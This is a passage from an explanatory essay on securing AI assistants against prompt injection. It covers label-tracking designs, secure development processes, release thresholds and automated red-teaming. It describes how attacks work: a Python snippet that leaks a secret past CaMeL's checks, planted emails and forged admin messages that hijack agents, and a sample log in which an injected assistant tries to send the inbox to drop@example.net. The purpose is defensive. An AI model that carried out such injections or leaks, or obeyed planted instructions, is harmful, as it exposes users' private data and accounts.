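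This is weak evidence, as the researchers acknowledge. They tested a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, on 24 tasks with one handwritten attack, and didn't use the kind of optimized search that defeated most of the defenses in *The Attacker Moves Second*. The adaptive attack did worse than the standard one, possibly because making the instruction sound routine made the agent less likely to follow it. LaunchSafe builds tools on the same principle, so it has an interest in the result. A fixed rule may still be harder to beat than a filter, because the attacker has to find a harmful action that the rule permits.

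### Gaps in the tracking

Garby and colleagues attacked the tracking itself. Their paper, first released in February and revised in July, describes two ways for a secret to escape CaMeL's labels. CaMeL correctly blocks a program that sends an email only if the user's bank balance is above some amount, because the decision to send depends on the balance. This version of their example gets around the check:

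```
rich = True
poor = True
if balance > 10000:
    poor = False
if poor:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("stranger@example.com", "rich")
```

Suppose the balance is 15,000. The program sets `poor` to False, and CaMeL labels `poor` secret because the change depended on the balance. The next branch doesn't run, so `rich` stays True and public, and the program sends the email. With a balance of 5,000, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out. The stranger can tell the two cases apart by whether the email arrives, although CaMeL never labeled `rich` secret. Researchers have known about this problem since the 1970s. Software that only monitors a program as it runs can't label a change the program would have made on a branch it didn't take.

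The other gap is outside the interpreter. If CaMeL blocks a program, ordinary Python code tries again, and nothing tracks the information that reaches that code. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it. Repeated attempts could reveal an entire 16-bit secret, such as a balance between 0 and 65,535.

A stranger would have trouble using either gap, because CaMeL's planner writes the program without reading the stranger's email. The gaps matter more if the user pastes hostile text into the request, or if an agent writes new code after reading untrusted data. They also show that an implementation can fall short of the guarantee its design suggests.

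*SPA* (2026) deals with untaken branches by checking the whole plan before it runs. Its verifier gives the steps in each branch the label of the condition that controls them. Such checks are harder to make for CaMeL's programs because Python, as *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) notes, lets a program change the types of its values and jump elsewhere when an error occurs.

Labels can also disappear when an agent saves something. In the earlier example of the poisoned newsletter, the agent read a hostile line on Monday and treated it as a trusted note on Thursday. *Flowsh* (2026) prevents this for agents that run shell commands by storing a label with each file and applying it to any later command that reads the file. Each file has only one label, so a single untrusted line makes the whole document untrusted.

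### Machine-checked guarantees

Garby and colleagues then built LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every value has a label that every operation updates. They proved a property called noninterference for all programs in the language that don't deliberately override a label. Roughly, it means that someone who can see only public results learns nothing from them about secret data, and that untrusted data can't affect trusted results. They wrote the proof in Lean, which checks each step by computer, and the proof covers the same software that calls the model. The guarantee doesn't rule out leaks that occur when a program stops or fails to finish. It also depends on the developer labeling the data sources correctly and putting checks on the sensitive tools.

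Strict noninterference would rule out useful tasks, so LLMbda has an `endorse` command that marks untrusted data as trusted. The planner has to write the command into the program, where a reviewer can find it. FIDES's exceptions are harder to review, because a reviewer can't tell from the log of one run whether a permitted yes-or-no answer was harmless or a leak.

The researchers' agent completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did when run without its policies. Across three models, only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The agent endorsed the file and paid the attacker. Without `endorse`, it would have refused, but it also couldn't have paid a genuine bill.

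In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (November 2026), Dongol looks for a definition that permits useful disclosures without an override. For example, a calendar assistant might send the user's free times to anyone who asks for a meeting. This violates noninterference because a stranger's email causes the assistant to reveal private data. Dongol compares the assistant with an imaginary twin that follows the same plan under the same checks, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The assistant is secure if everything an attacker can learn from it could also be learned from the twin.

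If a stranger emails the assistant an order to send the calendar and it obeys, the assistant still passes, because the stranger could have learned the same thing by asking for a meeting. If it also obeys an order to send a password reset code, it fails, because no email would make the twin do that.

Dongol then proves what he calls a fence theorem. Any plan is secure in this sense if, when the agent first reads untrusted text, the software permanently withdraws every tool an injected instruction could use. The theorem gives a mathematical basis to David C's advice to drop an assistant's privileges once it has read a stranger's text. In one of Dongol's examples, the software withdraws the sending tool after the agent has read the email but before it fetches a secret. This is too late, because the agent may already have other private data in its memory.

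The proofs are also relevant to approval prompts. Suppose the user approves a reply, and the software treats this as permission to send the next email, whatever it contains. An injected instruction can use that permission to email private data, and the software then blocks the user's real reply because the permission has already been used. This attack fails if the approval covers only the exact text and recipient. An attacker who can measure when the reply arrives may still learn whether the private data was identical to the approved text.

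Dongol checked the theory and 25 example agents in Isabelle/HOL, a program for verifying proofs. The theorem assumes that each injected instruction causes a single tool call and that whether the model follows it doesn't depend on secrets or on the software's earlier responses. It doesn't cover attacks that do damage without leaking anything, such as deleting a message, or agents whose model chooses every call as it goes along, which is how the basic mail assistant works. Software that blocks every tool call would pass, so a developer has to measure usefulness separately.

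### Who writes the labels and policies

Each of these designs requires someone to decide which data is trusted and what each tool may do with it. Willison admires CaMeL but says that asking users to think about security policies makes him "deeply nervous", because he finds them hard himself after two decades of work on application security. Microsoft has built software that adds labels to existing MCP tools. For each tool, a developer has to describe the format of its results, write a function that carries the labels through the tool, and choose or write a policy.

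Part of this work can be automated. In MCP, a tool's description can specify whether the tool only reads data and whether it contacts outside systems. Microsoft suggests allowing tools that only read from a closed system, and always asking the user before a destructive action. This works only if the tool's description is accurate. *APPA* (2026) handles unlabeled tools by keeping a record of the unresolved source until an approved step gives its data a definite label.

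Other researchers derive the policy from what the agent is supposed to do. Conseca, by Lillian Tsai and Eugene Bagdasarian, uses trusted context to generate a policy for the current purpose, in a form that a person can check. In *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents*, Copty, Haiby and colleagues (2026) combine the company's rules, the agent's role and the developer's configuration, in that order of authority, into a profile of permitted tasks, tools and data. The profile excludes the user's request, because users can also make mistakes or misuse an agent. The software instead checks the request against the profile.

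Copty and colleagues, who work at Microsoft, had a model classify requests as legitimate, out of scope, abusive or malicious. With the profile, its average score across the four groups, which accounts for both missed cases and false alarms, rose from 45 to 79 percent. Most of the improvement was in recognizing requests outside the agent's job. This could help a developer write a policy, but it doesn't provide the guarantee of a fixed check because the model making the judgment is sometimes wrong.

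Labels can also be wrong from the start, for example when a user pastes in a stranger's text. Narisetty and colleagues expect real deployments to fail mainly by misidentifying where data came from.

### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

An assistant that is told "Please do what Anna asks" can't plan its actions before reading Anna's email. FIDES can offer a fixed list of actions, such as booking a room or sending a file, but Anna may want something that isn't on the list. Narisetty and colleagues call such tasks the deepest open problem in this area.

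*AGENTSYS* (Wen, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) lets the agent plan as it goes but restricts what comes back from each tool. The main agent starts a separate worker for a tool call and specifies the fields it needs, such as a date and an amount. The worker reads the full result but returns only those fields, so the rest of the text never enters the main agent's context. Ordinary software checks the format of the returned fields.

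AgentSys uses isolation to remove hostile text that would otherwise influence every later decision an agent makes. When Wen and colleagues attacked an undefended agent on tasks with four tool calls, an instruction in the first result succeeded 60.5 percent of the time, compared with 5.9 percent for one in the third. On AgentDojo, isolation alone reduced the attack success rate to 2.19 percent, and further checks reduced it to 0.78 percent. With the full defense and no attack, the agent completed 64.4 percent of tasks, compared with 63.5 percent without the defense. These figures suggest that an agent can keep most of its flexibility, but attacks can still succeed because a field that accepts free text can carry an instruction.

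### False content in a correct plan

A false account number in a stranger's email can still reach the summary without changing the agent's plan. The CaMeL paper explicitly excludes this kind of harm from what the system is meant to prevent.

Labels help if the false number reaches a tool. A payment policy can require a trusted account number, so the software would block the payment or ask the user, as it did with the invoice address. Labels help less if the user reads the number and makes the payment by hand. The software could mark the number as coming from an unknown sender, but the user still has to notice the mark and decide whether to believe the number. Labels also don't show when a trusted source is wrong.

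### Adoption in products

Microsoft has gone furthest in putting these ideas into products. Its *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced in May that FIDES was available as an experimental part of Agent Framework, Microsoft's toolkit for building agents. In its example, an agent sorts bug reports in a public code repository. One report contains instructions to read a file of passwords and post the contents as a comment. Even if the model follows them, the software labels the file private and blocks the public comment or asks the user to approve it.

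If a developer forgets to label a tool, the software treats its results as trusted and public by default. Once untrusted text enters the main model's context, everything later in the run also counts as untrusted unless the developer removes that text. By default, the software avoids this by hiding untrusted results in variables, which requires extra calls to a quarantined model. If developers turn each blocked call into an approval prompt, users may again click through the prompts out of habit.

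Microsoft and GitHub have also added experimental tracking to GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal. Users have to switch the tracking on, and it covers only some tools from GitHub's own MCP server. That server can label material from public repositories as public and untrusted, and material from private ones as private and trusted. This is a workable first guess, but someone can copy an outsider's text into a private repository, where it would count as trusted.

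In Chrome, Google has borrowed from the two-model pattern and CaMeL. Parker describes a second model, the User Alignment Critic, that reviews each action the browser agent proposes and can veto it. The critic sees only a description of the action, not the unfiltered web page, so text on a hostile page can't reach it directly. But the critic is still a model judging whether an action fits the user's goal, and a purchase with the wrong delivery address may look like a reasonable step in a shopping task.

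## Building security into rapid releases

Labels, narrow permissions and approval prompts protect a product only if each new release keeps them intact, and companies change AI features every few weeks. Microsoft faced a similar conflict between features and security about 25 years ago, and at first responded by stopping work.

### The Windows stoppage

In 2001 two worms (programs that copy themselves from computer to computer), Code Red and Nimda, hit Microsoft products. Michael Howard recalls in Microsoft's collection of memories from the period that the worms made some customers rethink their use of the company's web server. Howard's team had been advising individual product groups, but this didn't scale, and the groups kept asking the same questions. That autumn the engineers building .NET, Microsoft's new software platform, paused development to take security training and look for flaws.

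Bill Gates then made security a priority for the whole company. In a memo on January 15, 2002, he told employees that when they had to choose between adding features and fixing security problems, "we need to choose security." The Register, which published the full memo in *MS' highest priority must be security* (2002), was skeptical. Gates had praised a change to the Outlook mail program that blocked viruses, but Microsoft had made it only after years of public embarrassment.

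More than 8,500 engineers stopped their regular work for two months to examine millions of lines of Windows code, according to *Microsoft Spent $100M on Trustworthy Computing* (Olavsrud, 2002). Microsoft had planned for 30 days, but the stoppage took nearly twice that and cost more than $100 million.

No company can do this before every release, so Microsoft spread the work across ordinary development. Its Security Development Lifecycle (SDL), first made mandatory in 2004, requires security activities at each stage of building software. *The Trustworthy Computing Security Development Lifecycle* (Lipner and Howard, 2005) describes the stages. A product team gets a security adviser when it starts planning. It writes a threat model during design, scans and reviews its code while programming, and reviews the code again during beta testing. A separate team then carries out a Final Security Review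 two to six months before the software is complete.

In threat modeling, engineers list what a system has to protect, how an attacker could reach it, and what would stop the attack. Microsoft's security team considered this the most valuable part of the Security Development Lifecycle (SDL). The team had less faith in penetration testing, in which experts try to break into a nearly finished product. If they found many flaws, the product team was supposed to fix them and work out why the earlier stages had missed them.

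### Before-and-after counts

Microsoft publishes a security bulletin when it patches a flaw. In *Security Progress at Microsoft*, Microsoft gives these counts:

| Product | Periods compared | Bulletins before | Bulletins after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Windows 2000 Server and Windows Server 2003 | First 320 days of each, critical or important bulletins only | 40 | 9 |
| SQL Server 2000 | 15 months before and after Service Pack 3 | 13 | 3 |
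| Exchange 2000 | 21 months before and after Service Pack 3 | 7 | 1 |

The Windows figures amount to a 78 percent drop in bulletins. In an interview for Microsoft's press site, Howard said there were 63 percent fewer critical or important vulnerabilities in the first year. Both figures can be right, because a bulletin can cover several vulnerabilities.

Chance probably doesn't explain the drops. If each of the eight Exchange bulletins had been equally likely to fall before or after the service pack, there would have been only a 3.5 percent chance of at least seven falling before it. But the counts are weak evidence that the new process caused the drops. Windows Server 2003 differed from its predecessor in many ways, and nobody built a version without the process for comparison. Microsoft also applied its severity ratings to the Windows 2000 bulletins retroactively.

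SQL Server and Exchange were the same products before and after the security work, but outsiders may already have found their easiest flaws. Companies also tend to start a cleanup after a bad period, so the numbers might have improved anyway. All three products came out before the SDL became mandatory, so the counts mostly reflect the early security drives. Lipner and Howard called conclusive claims "premature".

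### Adapting the SDL to short cycles

The Final Security Review was designed for software that would barely change for months before release. This no longer held once Microsoft adopted agile development, in which teams release small changes in short cycles, and began running cloud services. Mark Cartwright, a security manager, recalls in Microsoft's collection that the company had to make major changes to its threat modeling, its tools, and its "bug bar", the standard for deciding which flaws are serious enough to fix before release.

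Microsoft's *Evolving Microsoft Security Development Lifecycle (SDL)* describes continuous SDL, its current approach for services that ship daily or several times a day. Tools scan the code throughout development. A central system collects the results, checks them against the requirements and stores the evidence, so a reviewer can later see why a release passed. In a pilot of one scanning tool, teams resolved 92 percent of the problems on time, though this doesn't show that the services became harder to attack.

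Microsoft also changes the requirements. In 2023 it added six, retired six and substantially revised 19. It still recommends human review for the most critical products, where an automated scan is least likely to be enough.

### Making the safe query the default

Scanning finds mistakes after developers make them. Google's security engineers wanted to prevent those mistakes because training had not worked well enough. *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, their account of the work, explains that a large program can contain hundreds of places where an injection flaw might occur, and that even developers who understand the flaw sometimes slip. Expert review also falls short because it covers one version of the software and is hard to repeat for every release.

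Kern (2025), in *Safe Coding*, shows how Google changed its programming tools instead. An ordinary database function accepts any string as a query, so both of these programs run:

```
q1 := "SELECT y FROM table WHERE x = ?"
db.Query(q1, inputX)

q2 := "SELECT y FROM table WHERE x = " + inputX
db.Query(q2)
```

The first uses a placeholder, while the second has the same flaw as the balance page. Google's version of the function accepts only a value of a special type, `TrustedSqlString`. Developers can create one only through approved functions, which accept text from trustworthy sources, such as text written directly in the source code. If a developer tries to add `inputX`, the program won't build, and the error message can point to the safe method. Code that needs an exception must be on a list that security experts control.

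*Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* reports that, about ten years earlier, Google found tens of cross-site scripting flaws a year in each large web application, such as Gmail. The total across all applications built on its safe frameworks then fell to the low single digits, and SQL injection became "essentially a nonissue" in its internal code. A small team maintains these tools for many thousands of developers.

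This is also a company's own before-and-after account, but its causal claim is easier to believe than the SDL's because the build rejects unsafe queries, except in some older code that is still exempt. Google can require its own teams to use the safe function, whereas the publisher of a public programming library can only encourage other companies to use it.

Google's experience fits David C's remark that SQL injection is now rare on websites. The flaw's second place on MITRE's list doesn't contradict this, because MITRE ranks flaws by combining the number of published vulnerabilities with their average severity.

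MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 10 KEV Weaknesses List Insights* ranks weaknesses that attackers are known to have exploited. SQL injection is not in the top ten, and operating system command injection rises from ninth to first. This fits David C's remark, though MITRE warns that some kinds of attack are harder to detect than others.

David C's remark that SQL injection is rare is plausible for sites built with modern frameworks, but not for commercial software in general. The *Secure by Design Alert* from CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, and the FBI followed attacks that exploited SQL injection flaws in a file transfer product and affected thousands of organizations. In July 2025, CISA added a SQL injection flaw in FortiWeb, a product meant to protect web applications, to its *Known Exploited Vulnerabilities Catalog*.

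Good defaults don't spread on their own, either. *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (Zorz, 2026) reports that three of today's ten most common weaknesses would already have counted as "unforgivable" under a standard MITRE proposed in 2007. CISA blames organizational culture and wants software makers to remove whole classes of flaw during development.

### What changes with a model

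Google's check works because a program's behavior depends on code that the build tools can inspect. But an AI feature's behavior can change while its code stays the same. In Anthropic's September coding test, for example, Shade succeeded more often against Opus 5 than against Fable 5.1. Switching a product between them might change only the model's name in a settings file, or nothing at all if the provider made the switch, so a code scanner would find nothing to report.

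A new connector, which links the assistant to another service, can also make existing permissions more dangerous. A rough count of the ways to steal data is:

```
routes = untrusted sources × private stores × ways to send data out
```

Suppose the mail assistant reads three untrusted sources (email, calendar invitations and shared files) and can see three private stores (mail, files and appointments). Each route for stealing data combines one source, one store and one way to send data out. If the assistant has no sending tool, there are 3 × 3 × 0 = 0 routes. Adding one creates nine, and if the next release lets the assistant read web pages, there are 12. The routes aren't equally dangerous, but reviewing only the new tool isn't enough, because even flawless sending code could let an attacker steal data through any of the earlier sources.

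Tests of a model also give less definite results. The balance page either always treats the hostile name as data or never does, but a model may resist an attack nine times and follow it on the tenth. Microsoft's *Proactively identifying, assessing, and addressing risk in AI systems* points out that a one-in-a-million interaction can occur thousands of times a day in a global product.

Microsoft advises teams to rank possible failures by how much harm they would do and to use their likelihood to choose a response. People can handle rare but severe failures, while frequent failures need automated controls. Microsoft objects to the usual method of multiplying harm by likelihood because it makes severe risks look small when they are rare. The multiplication is sound if the team counts every use of the product, but few teams can estimate the likelihood of a very rare failure well enough to rely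 on the result.

### Microsoft's SDL for AI

In February 2026, Microsoft announced an extension of its secure development process in *Microsoft SDL: Evolving security practices for an AI-powered world*. Microsoft acknowledges that model updates, new tools and changes in agents' behavior outpace traditional reviews. The extension covers six topics: threat modeling, monitoring of AI systems, protection of their memory, agents' identities and permissions, model releases, and shutdown mechanisms.

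These are sensible topics, but the announcement contains little that a team could apply. It sets no release criteria and doesn't specify who must review a new tool or which test results should stop a release. Much of it describes six "pillars", such as research, collaboration and continuous improvement. Microsoft promised practical guidance on each topic in the coming months. The 2005 account of the original SDL was far more specific about who reviewed a product and when, though Microsoft had three years of experience by then.

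Microsoft gives more concrete advice on identifying risks in advance. It tells teams to map where untrusted data enters, decide what the system must never do, and plan how to detect and respond to failures. It also recommends limiting tool permissions, listing permitted destinations, and requiring human approval for irreversible actions. These recommendations would help a team design a feature, but they still don't set a threshold for releasing it.

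### A process for weekly releases

A team that ships every week can't hold a full review each time, but it can decide in advance which changes require one:

| Change in the release | Work before release |
|---|---|
| Layout or wording of the interface | Ordinary automated tests |
| New source of data | Short threat model, and attacks planted in that source |
| New tool, or wider permissions for an existing one | Short threat model, tests of the new combinations, and an off switch |
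| New model, or new instructions for the model | Short threat model, and the full set of attack tests again |

The threat model can be a page long if the team keeps one for the whole product and updates only the parts that changed. It should record who can write the new input, what the assistant can now do with it, the worst plausible result, and what would prevent that result if the assistant followed an attacker's instructions.

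Suppose the mail assistant can draft replies, but the user has to copy them into the mail program. The team wants to add a "send" button below each draft. Anyone who can email the user, send them an invitation or share a file with them can influence the draft. In the worst plausible case, a stranger's email gets the assistant to put private information in a reply, and the user sends it without reading it closely.

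The team also has to decide whether the model or ordinary software sends the draft. If the model has a sending tool, a hostile email can trigger a tool call before the user does anything. If ordinary software sends the draft after the user clicks a button, the model can affect only what the user sees. The second design is safer, even though both could show the same button, so the team adopts a rule that the model must never be able to send mail itself.

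### Shared components with safe defaults

The team can enforce that rule with a type, as Google does for queries:

```
send_email(draft: ApprovedDraft)
```

Only the code that handles a real click can create an `ApprovedDraft`, using the exact recipients, text and attachments on the screen. The model's output is an ordinary string, so code that tries to send it directly won't build. The click handler must also reject clicks made by scripts, a check missing from Claude for Chrome. Because the browser and the mail server run separate programs, the server must verify the approval too and refuse any message that changed after the click.

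Other teams can then use the same component for meeting invitations or shared documents. They get its protections without designing them, and security experts can review one piece of code thoroughly instead of many pieces quickly. If someone finds a flaw, one fix covers every product that uses the component.

By default, the component should allow replies only to addresses the user has written to before, a rule modeled on Office's macro block. Allowing replies to anyone already in the conversation is less safe, because that includes an attacker who sent the first email. The component should also show everything it will send, since a draft could contain hidden text.

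The type proves that someone clicked, but not that they read the draft. Google's type gives a stronger guarantee because it keeps outside text out of the query's structure. Type checking cannot determine whether a sentence in an email contains something the user would rather keep private.

### Release thresholds

Lipner and Howard describe "ship criteria", conditions software must meet before release. Some criteria for the send button can be absolute. Nothing goes out without a click, and changing the recipient cancels the approval. Ordinary software enforces these rules, so a single failure should stop the release.

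The model needs a different kind of threshold, such as the share of hostile emails that get private information into a draft. If the team will accept at most 0.5 percent, it needs about 600 attempts without a failure to be 95 percent confident that the true rate is lower:

```
(1 - 0.005)^600 ≈ 0.05
```

With only 200 attempts, a model that fails 0.5 percent of the time would get a perfect score 37 percent of the time. If the team reran the test after each failure, that model would pass at least once in three tries about 75 percent of the time. So the team should set the threshold and the number of attempts before testing, and investigate a failure instead of rerunning the test. The 600 attempts also need to cover many different scenarios, not variations on one email.

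The right failure threshold depends on how the model's output is used. If users send nine out of ten faulty drafts without noticing the problem, a 0.5 percent failure rate in drafts becomes 0.45 percent in sent mail. A button that sends the draft needs a stricter threshold than a feature that only writes it, even though the model and its output are the same.

### Staged rollout and off switches

In a staged rollout, the team releases a feature to a small group, then to more people if nothing goes wrong. The send button might go to employees first, then to 1 percent of customers, and then to everyone. The original SDL had a related rule that features most people didn't need should be off by default or open to only a few users.

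A first week without reported problems is weak evidence that the feature is safe. Suppose those customers send 50,000 messages with the button, and one in 10,000 contains private information the user didn't mean to send. The team should expect five such messages. If users notice and report only one in ten, the team has about a 61 percent chance of getting no reports. An attacker may also wait until everyone has the feature before exploiting it.

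The team can therefore expand what the button does as well as who has it. At first it might send only plain text to colleagues, and then to other known addresses. Later it might also send to new addresses or include attachments. Each step gives the team a chance to find problems while the possible harm is still limited.

An off switch is a setting that ordinary software checks before each use of a tool. The send button needs its own off switch so that the team can disable sending without disabling summaries and drafts. A single switch for the whole assistant would be simpler, but a team would hesitate to use it on uncertain evidence because every user would lose the assistant entirely.

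The server should check whether sending has been switched off, because some users will have an old version of the app open. It should also check this for messages already waiting to go out, and refuse to send if it can't read the setting. The team has to practise using the switch and decide who may use it at night without asking a manager. The team can undo a bad model update by returning to the previous model, but only if the provider still offers it.

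### ETSI and OWASP guidance

Published guidance can help a team find gaps in this process. TS 104 223, a standard from the European standards body ETSI, sets baseline security requirements for AI models and systems. David C aligns his advice with it under four headings: awareness among developers and the organization, secure design, making attacks harder, and monitoring. For the send button, awareness means that the product manager, as well as the security team, knows that some injection risk will remain. Secure design includes the threat model and `ApprovedDraft`, while model training and filters make attacks harder. Monitoring continues after release, along with automated red teaming and bug bounties.

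OWASP's lists work better as reminders during threat modeling. Its list for language model applications puts prompt injection first, and also gives the team a reason to check how the draft appears on the screen. A team shouldn't stop after the first few entries, because the ranking doesn't reflect the risk to a particular product. OWASP has a separate list for agents, which Microsoft has matched to protections in Copilot Studio, its tool for building agents. That list becomes more relevant if the team later lets the assistant send mail without a click.

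### Shipping early and learning

There are good reasons to release a feature before the team has answered every question. Real users will try things no tester thought of, and a long review may examine a model that the company replaces before release. Frequent releases also help with security, because a team that can ship on any day can fix a flaw quickly. A company that delays may lose users to a competitor with weaker protections.

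The history of SQL injection partly supports this view, since the industry did learn from its mistakes. But learning took a decade of breaches, and the people whose data leaked had not agreed to that risk. David C warns that AI features could cause a similar wave of breaches. Fixing the problem later was also expensive, as the Windows stoppage showed.

To learn from an early release, the team also has to see what went wrong. Users will complain about a clumsy summary, but they may never find out that a reply leaked a confidential figure. Early release therefore makes most sense when mistakes are easy to see and undo, so it usually suits a feature that drafts email better than one that sends it.

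The team could ship the drafts first and, with users' permission, measure what users delete from them before sending a reply by hand. If users often delete account numbers or details from other people's messages, the button isn't ready, and the team has learned this before any of that information went out.

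## Continuous testing, monitoring and patching

A review before launch can't cover later changes to the product or attacks that nobody has written yet. Some companies therefore attack their own products all the time, in a loop:

1. People or software write new attacks.
2. The team runs each attack on a realistic copy of the product and checks whether the harm really occurs.
3. Engineers retrain the model or change the software around it.
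4. The team keeps the attack as a test for later releases.
5. The search starts again on the repaired product.

The copy in step 2 needs working tools and fake data. A mail assistant may write "I have forwarded the invoice" without issuing a tool call, or forward the invoice without mentioning it, so the team has to check the test outbox rather than the reply.

### OpenAI's attacker for Atlas

The agent in OpenAI's Atlas browser can click and type in the user's accounts. To find attacks on it, OpenAI trained a language model with reinforcement learning. The training rewarded the model for making the agent complete a harmful task, such as sending an email or moving money, that could take tens or hundreds of steps.

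Before settling on an attack, the attacking model sends a draft to a simulator, which runs the agent on it and returns the agent's reasoning and actions. The attacking model then revises the draft and tries again. OpenAI doesn't show users the agent's reasoning, so outside attackers have less information to use.

In one case, the attacker put an email in a test inbox with instructions for the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email, sent the resignation and never wrote the reply. OpenAI advises users to give agents specific instructions, but this user's request was already specific. It would have helped more if the agent had asked for confirmation before sending, as OpenAI says its agents should.

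OpenAI trained a new version of the agent on the attacks it had found and released it to all Atlas users by December 22, 2025. It also uses records of successful attacks to improve monitoring and other safeguards outside the model. The announcement is evidence that the attacker finds real failures, but it includes no attack success rates from before or after the update, so readers can't tell from it how much the retraining helped.

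Charlie Eriksen of Aikido Security said such testing can catch obvious failures but doesn't "change the underlying dynamic" (quoted in Nolan, 2025, *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas*). The resignation email was not an obvious failure, but he has a point, because the retrained agent could still email the chief executive. Retraining had changed only its tendency to obey a stranger.

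### How GPT-Red trains

OpenAI's next attacker, GPT-Red, trains alongside the models it attacks, through a method called self-play (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026, *GPT-Red*). In each round, the training software picks a task for a defending model and a place where an outsider could insert text, such as a search result. It also gives GPT-Red a harmful goal, such as deleting a folder or sending an access key to an outside server. GPT-Red drafts an attack, tests it on the defender and edits it until it judges the attack good enough or runs out of time.

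GPT-Red earns a reward if the final attack works and follows the rules about what an outsider could change. The defender earns one if it resists the attack and finishes the user's task, so it can't do well by refusing everything. As each side improves, the other has to find new attacks or defenses.

The researchers used many defenders because an attacker facing only one tended to settle on a narrow kind of attack. They started GPT-Red from GPT-5.5 and used about as much computing power as the reinforcement learning for a recent production model.

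Scoring the attacks was difficult. In one exercise, the defender was told never to use symbols or pictograms. The attacker asked for a reply in Chinese, and the scoring code counted the Chinese characters as a violation. A team that skips step 2 of the loop could spend weeks fixing false failures like this one.

GPT-Red also worked outside the laboratory, against Vendy, an agent that runs a vending machine in OpenAI's office and talks to customers on Slack. After practicing on a simulation, GPT-Red sent Vendy a message with forged details identifying the sender as a trusted administrator. Vendy cut the price of an expensive item to 50 cents, ordered a new item worth over $100 to sell for 50 cents, and canceled another customer's order. Software that took the sender's identity from Slack's own records could have blocked this attack without changing the model.

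### The comparison with human red-teamers

OpenAI's announcement *GPT‑Red* (2026) reports that GPT-Red successfully attacked GPT-5.1, an OpenAI model from November 2025, in 84 percent of scenarios, compared with 13 percent for humans. OpenAI internally recreated the scenarios from Gray Swan's public competition, removed the human-written attacks and had GPT-Red write its own. GPT-Red had not trained on these scenarios, but it had trained against a range of earlier OpenAI models, possibly including GPT-5.1.

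The 13 percent human success rate probably understates the best that people can do. In the original competition, participants beat even the most resistant model in about a third of the scenarios, and it would be surprising if they had beaten GPT-5.1 in fewer. Wallace and colleagues describe the comparison as one of average success rates, so the human figure more likely reflects a typical submitted attack than the combined efforts of all 464 participants, who also divided their time among 13 models.

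Part of GPT-Red's lead comes from practicing on the target. GPT-5.5, which had no special training as an attacker, did about as well as the humans when it wrote a single attack without testing it. It did much better when it could test drafts on GPT-5.1, and GPT-Red did better still. This is good evidence that a trained attacker can search many scenarios more thoroughly than a company could afford to have people do, but not that people are no longer needed.

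### What the defender's own attacker can miss

GPT-Red's rules let it change one tool result or a few unimportant files, but not privileged files such as AGENTS.md, which holds standing instructions for a coding agent. Yet a developer who downloads a stranger's project may also get the stranger's version of that file. The rules also exclude attacks divided between two emails. Wallace and colleagues acknowledge that GPT-Red has had less training on images and on attacks spread over several turns, and that people may find kinds of attack it never tries.

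Some serious flaws involve no clever wording. For example, Claude for Chrome accepted a forged click, and EchoLeak sent data out through a Teams service that forwarded requests. A model rewarded for writing persuasive text is unlikely to look for either kind of flaw.

The attacking and defending models may also share blind spots, since one company trained both. GPT-5.6 Sol, which was trained on GPT-Red's attacks, failed against only 0.05 percent of GPT-Red's direct injections. On Gray Swan's July benchmark, attackers succeeded against the same model 20 percent of the time within 15 attempts. The tests differ too much to compare directly, but outsiders still had attacks that worked.

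Collecting attacks from outsiders can be cheap. The competition's $40,000 in prizes comes to less than $5 for each of its 8,648 successful attacks, not counting the cost of running it. Dziemian and colleagues note that a small number of skilled participants disproportionately influenced the results, so attracting such people matters more to a company than attracting a large number of participants.

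### Regression tests for injection

A regression test checks that an old fault has not come back. For the balance page, a developer can submit the hostile name once and check that the query returns nothing. A prompt injection test has to recreate the whole situation, which in the resignation case means the planted email, the user's request and the agent's tools. The test then checks that the out-of-office reply exists and that no letter has gone to the chief executive.

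Testing an attack once isn't enough. If it still works 10 percent of the time, the team needs 29 runs for a 95 percent chance of seeing it succeed at least once.

A model can also learn to resist only the exact wording of stored attacks, so the team needs new variations. OpenAI ranked a set of GPT-Red's attacks by how often they succeeded, trained GPT-5.6 on the weaker half and kept the stronger half for testing. It also excluded every agentic coding scenario from this training. GPT-5.6 resisted between just over 50 percent and 89 percent of attacks in the held-out tests, although Wallace and colleagues warn that scoring errors prevent any model from reaching 100 percent on some tests.

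The surrounding software needs a different test. The team can replace the model with a short script that always issues the hostile tool call, such as sending an invoice to an unknown address. If the server blocks the call, the team has checked the restriction without relying on the model's variable output, and the result still holds when the company changes models. The test collection should also include ordinary requests that the feature should fulfill, such as a resignation letter for a user who really wants to resign.

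Small teams can build on existing tests. Dziemian and colleagues published their testing software and 95 attacks that had worked on Qwen, and they offer evaluations on a larger set of 2,679 attacks. They chose the 95 because none worked on any closed commercial model, so resisting them all is very weak evidence that a commercial model is secure.

### What to log

Monitoring may reveal attacks that a team didn't think to test for. David C recommends logging enough to identify suspicious activity, potentially including the model's full input and output, its tool use and its calls to other services. He singles out failed calls, because an attacker will probably have to refine an attack before it works.

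Suppose a stranger's email tells the mail assistant to export the inbox. The stranger doesn't know which tools the assistant has, so the log might contain:

```
10:02:11  read_message  id=8841                  allowed
10:02:14  export_inbox  to=drop@example.net      failed: no such tool
10:02:15  send_mail     to=drop@example.net      blocked: new address
```

Nothing has leaked, but the model has tried to send something nobody asked for. The team can use the message number to find the email, remove it from other inboxes and add it to its tests. If nobody checks the log, the stranger's next email may name the right tool. The log should also record which versions of the model and its instructions were running, or the team may not be able to reproduce the failure.

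Most failed tool calls have harmless causes. If a product makes a million tool calls a day and 1 percent fail because the model misspelled a name or a server was busy, the team has 10,000 failures a day to sort through. Patterns can help distinguish attacks from these errors, such as several users' assistants trying to reach the same unknown address, or failures that always follow the same message. OpenAI also uses techniques it observes in real attacks in its ongoing testing.

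A log that shows no suspicious activity doesn't prove that nobody is attacking, because an attacker can practise on another product or on a model running at home and then send an email that works the first time. Dziemian and colleagues consider an agent's records too long and complex for people to inspect effectively, so the developer may have to use software to read them. If that software is a language model, it will read the hostile email too, so it shouldn't have tools of its own.

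### The privacy cost of full logs

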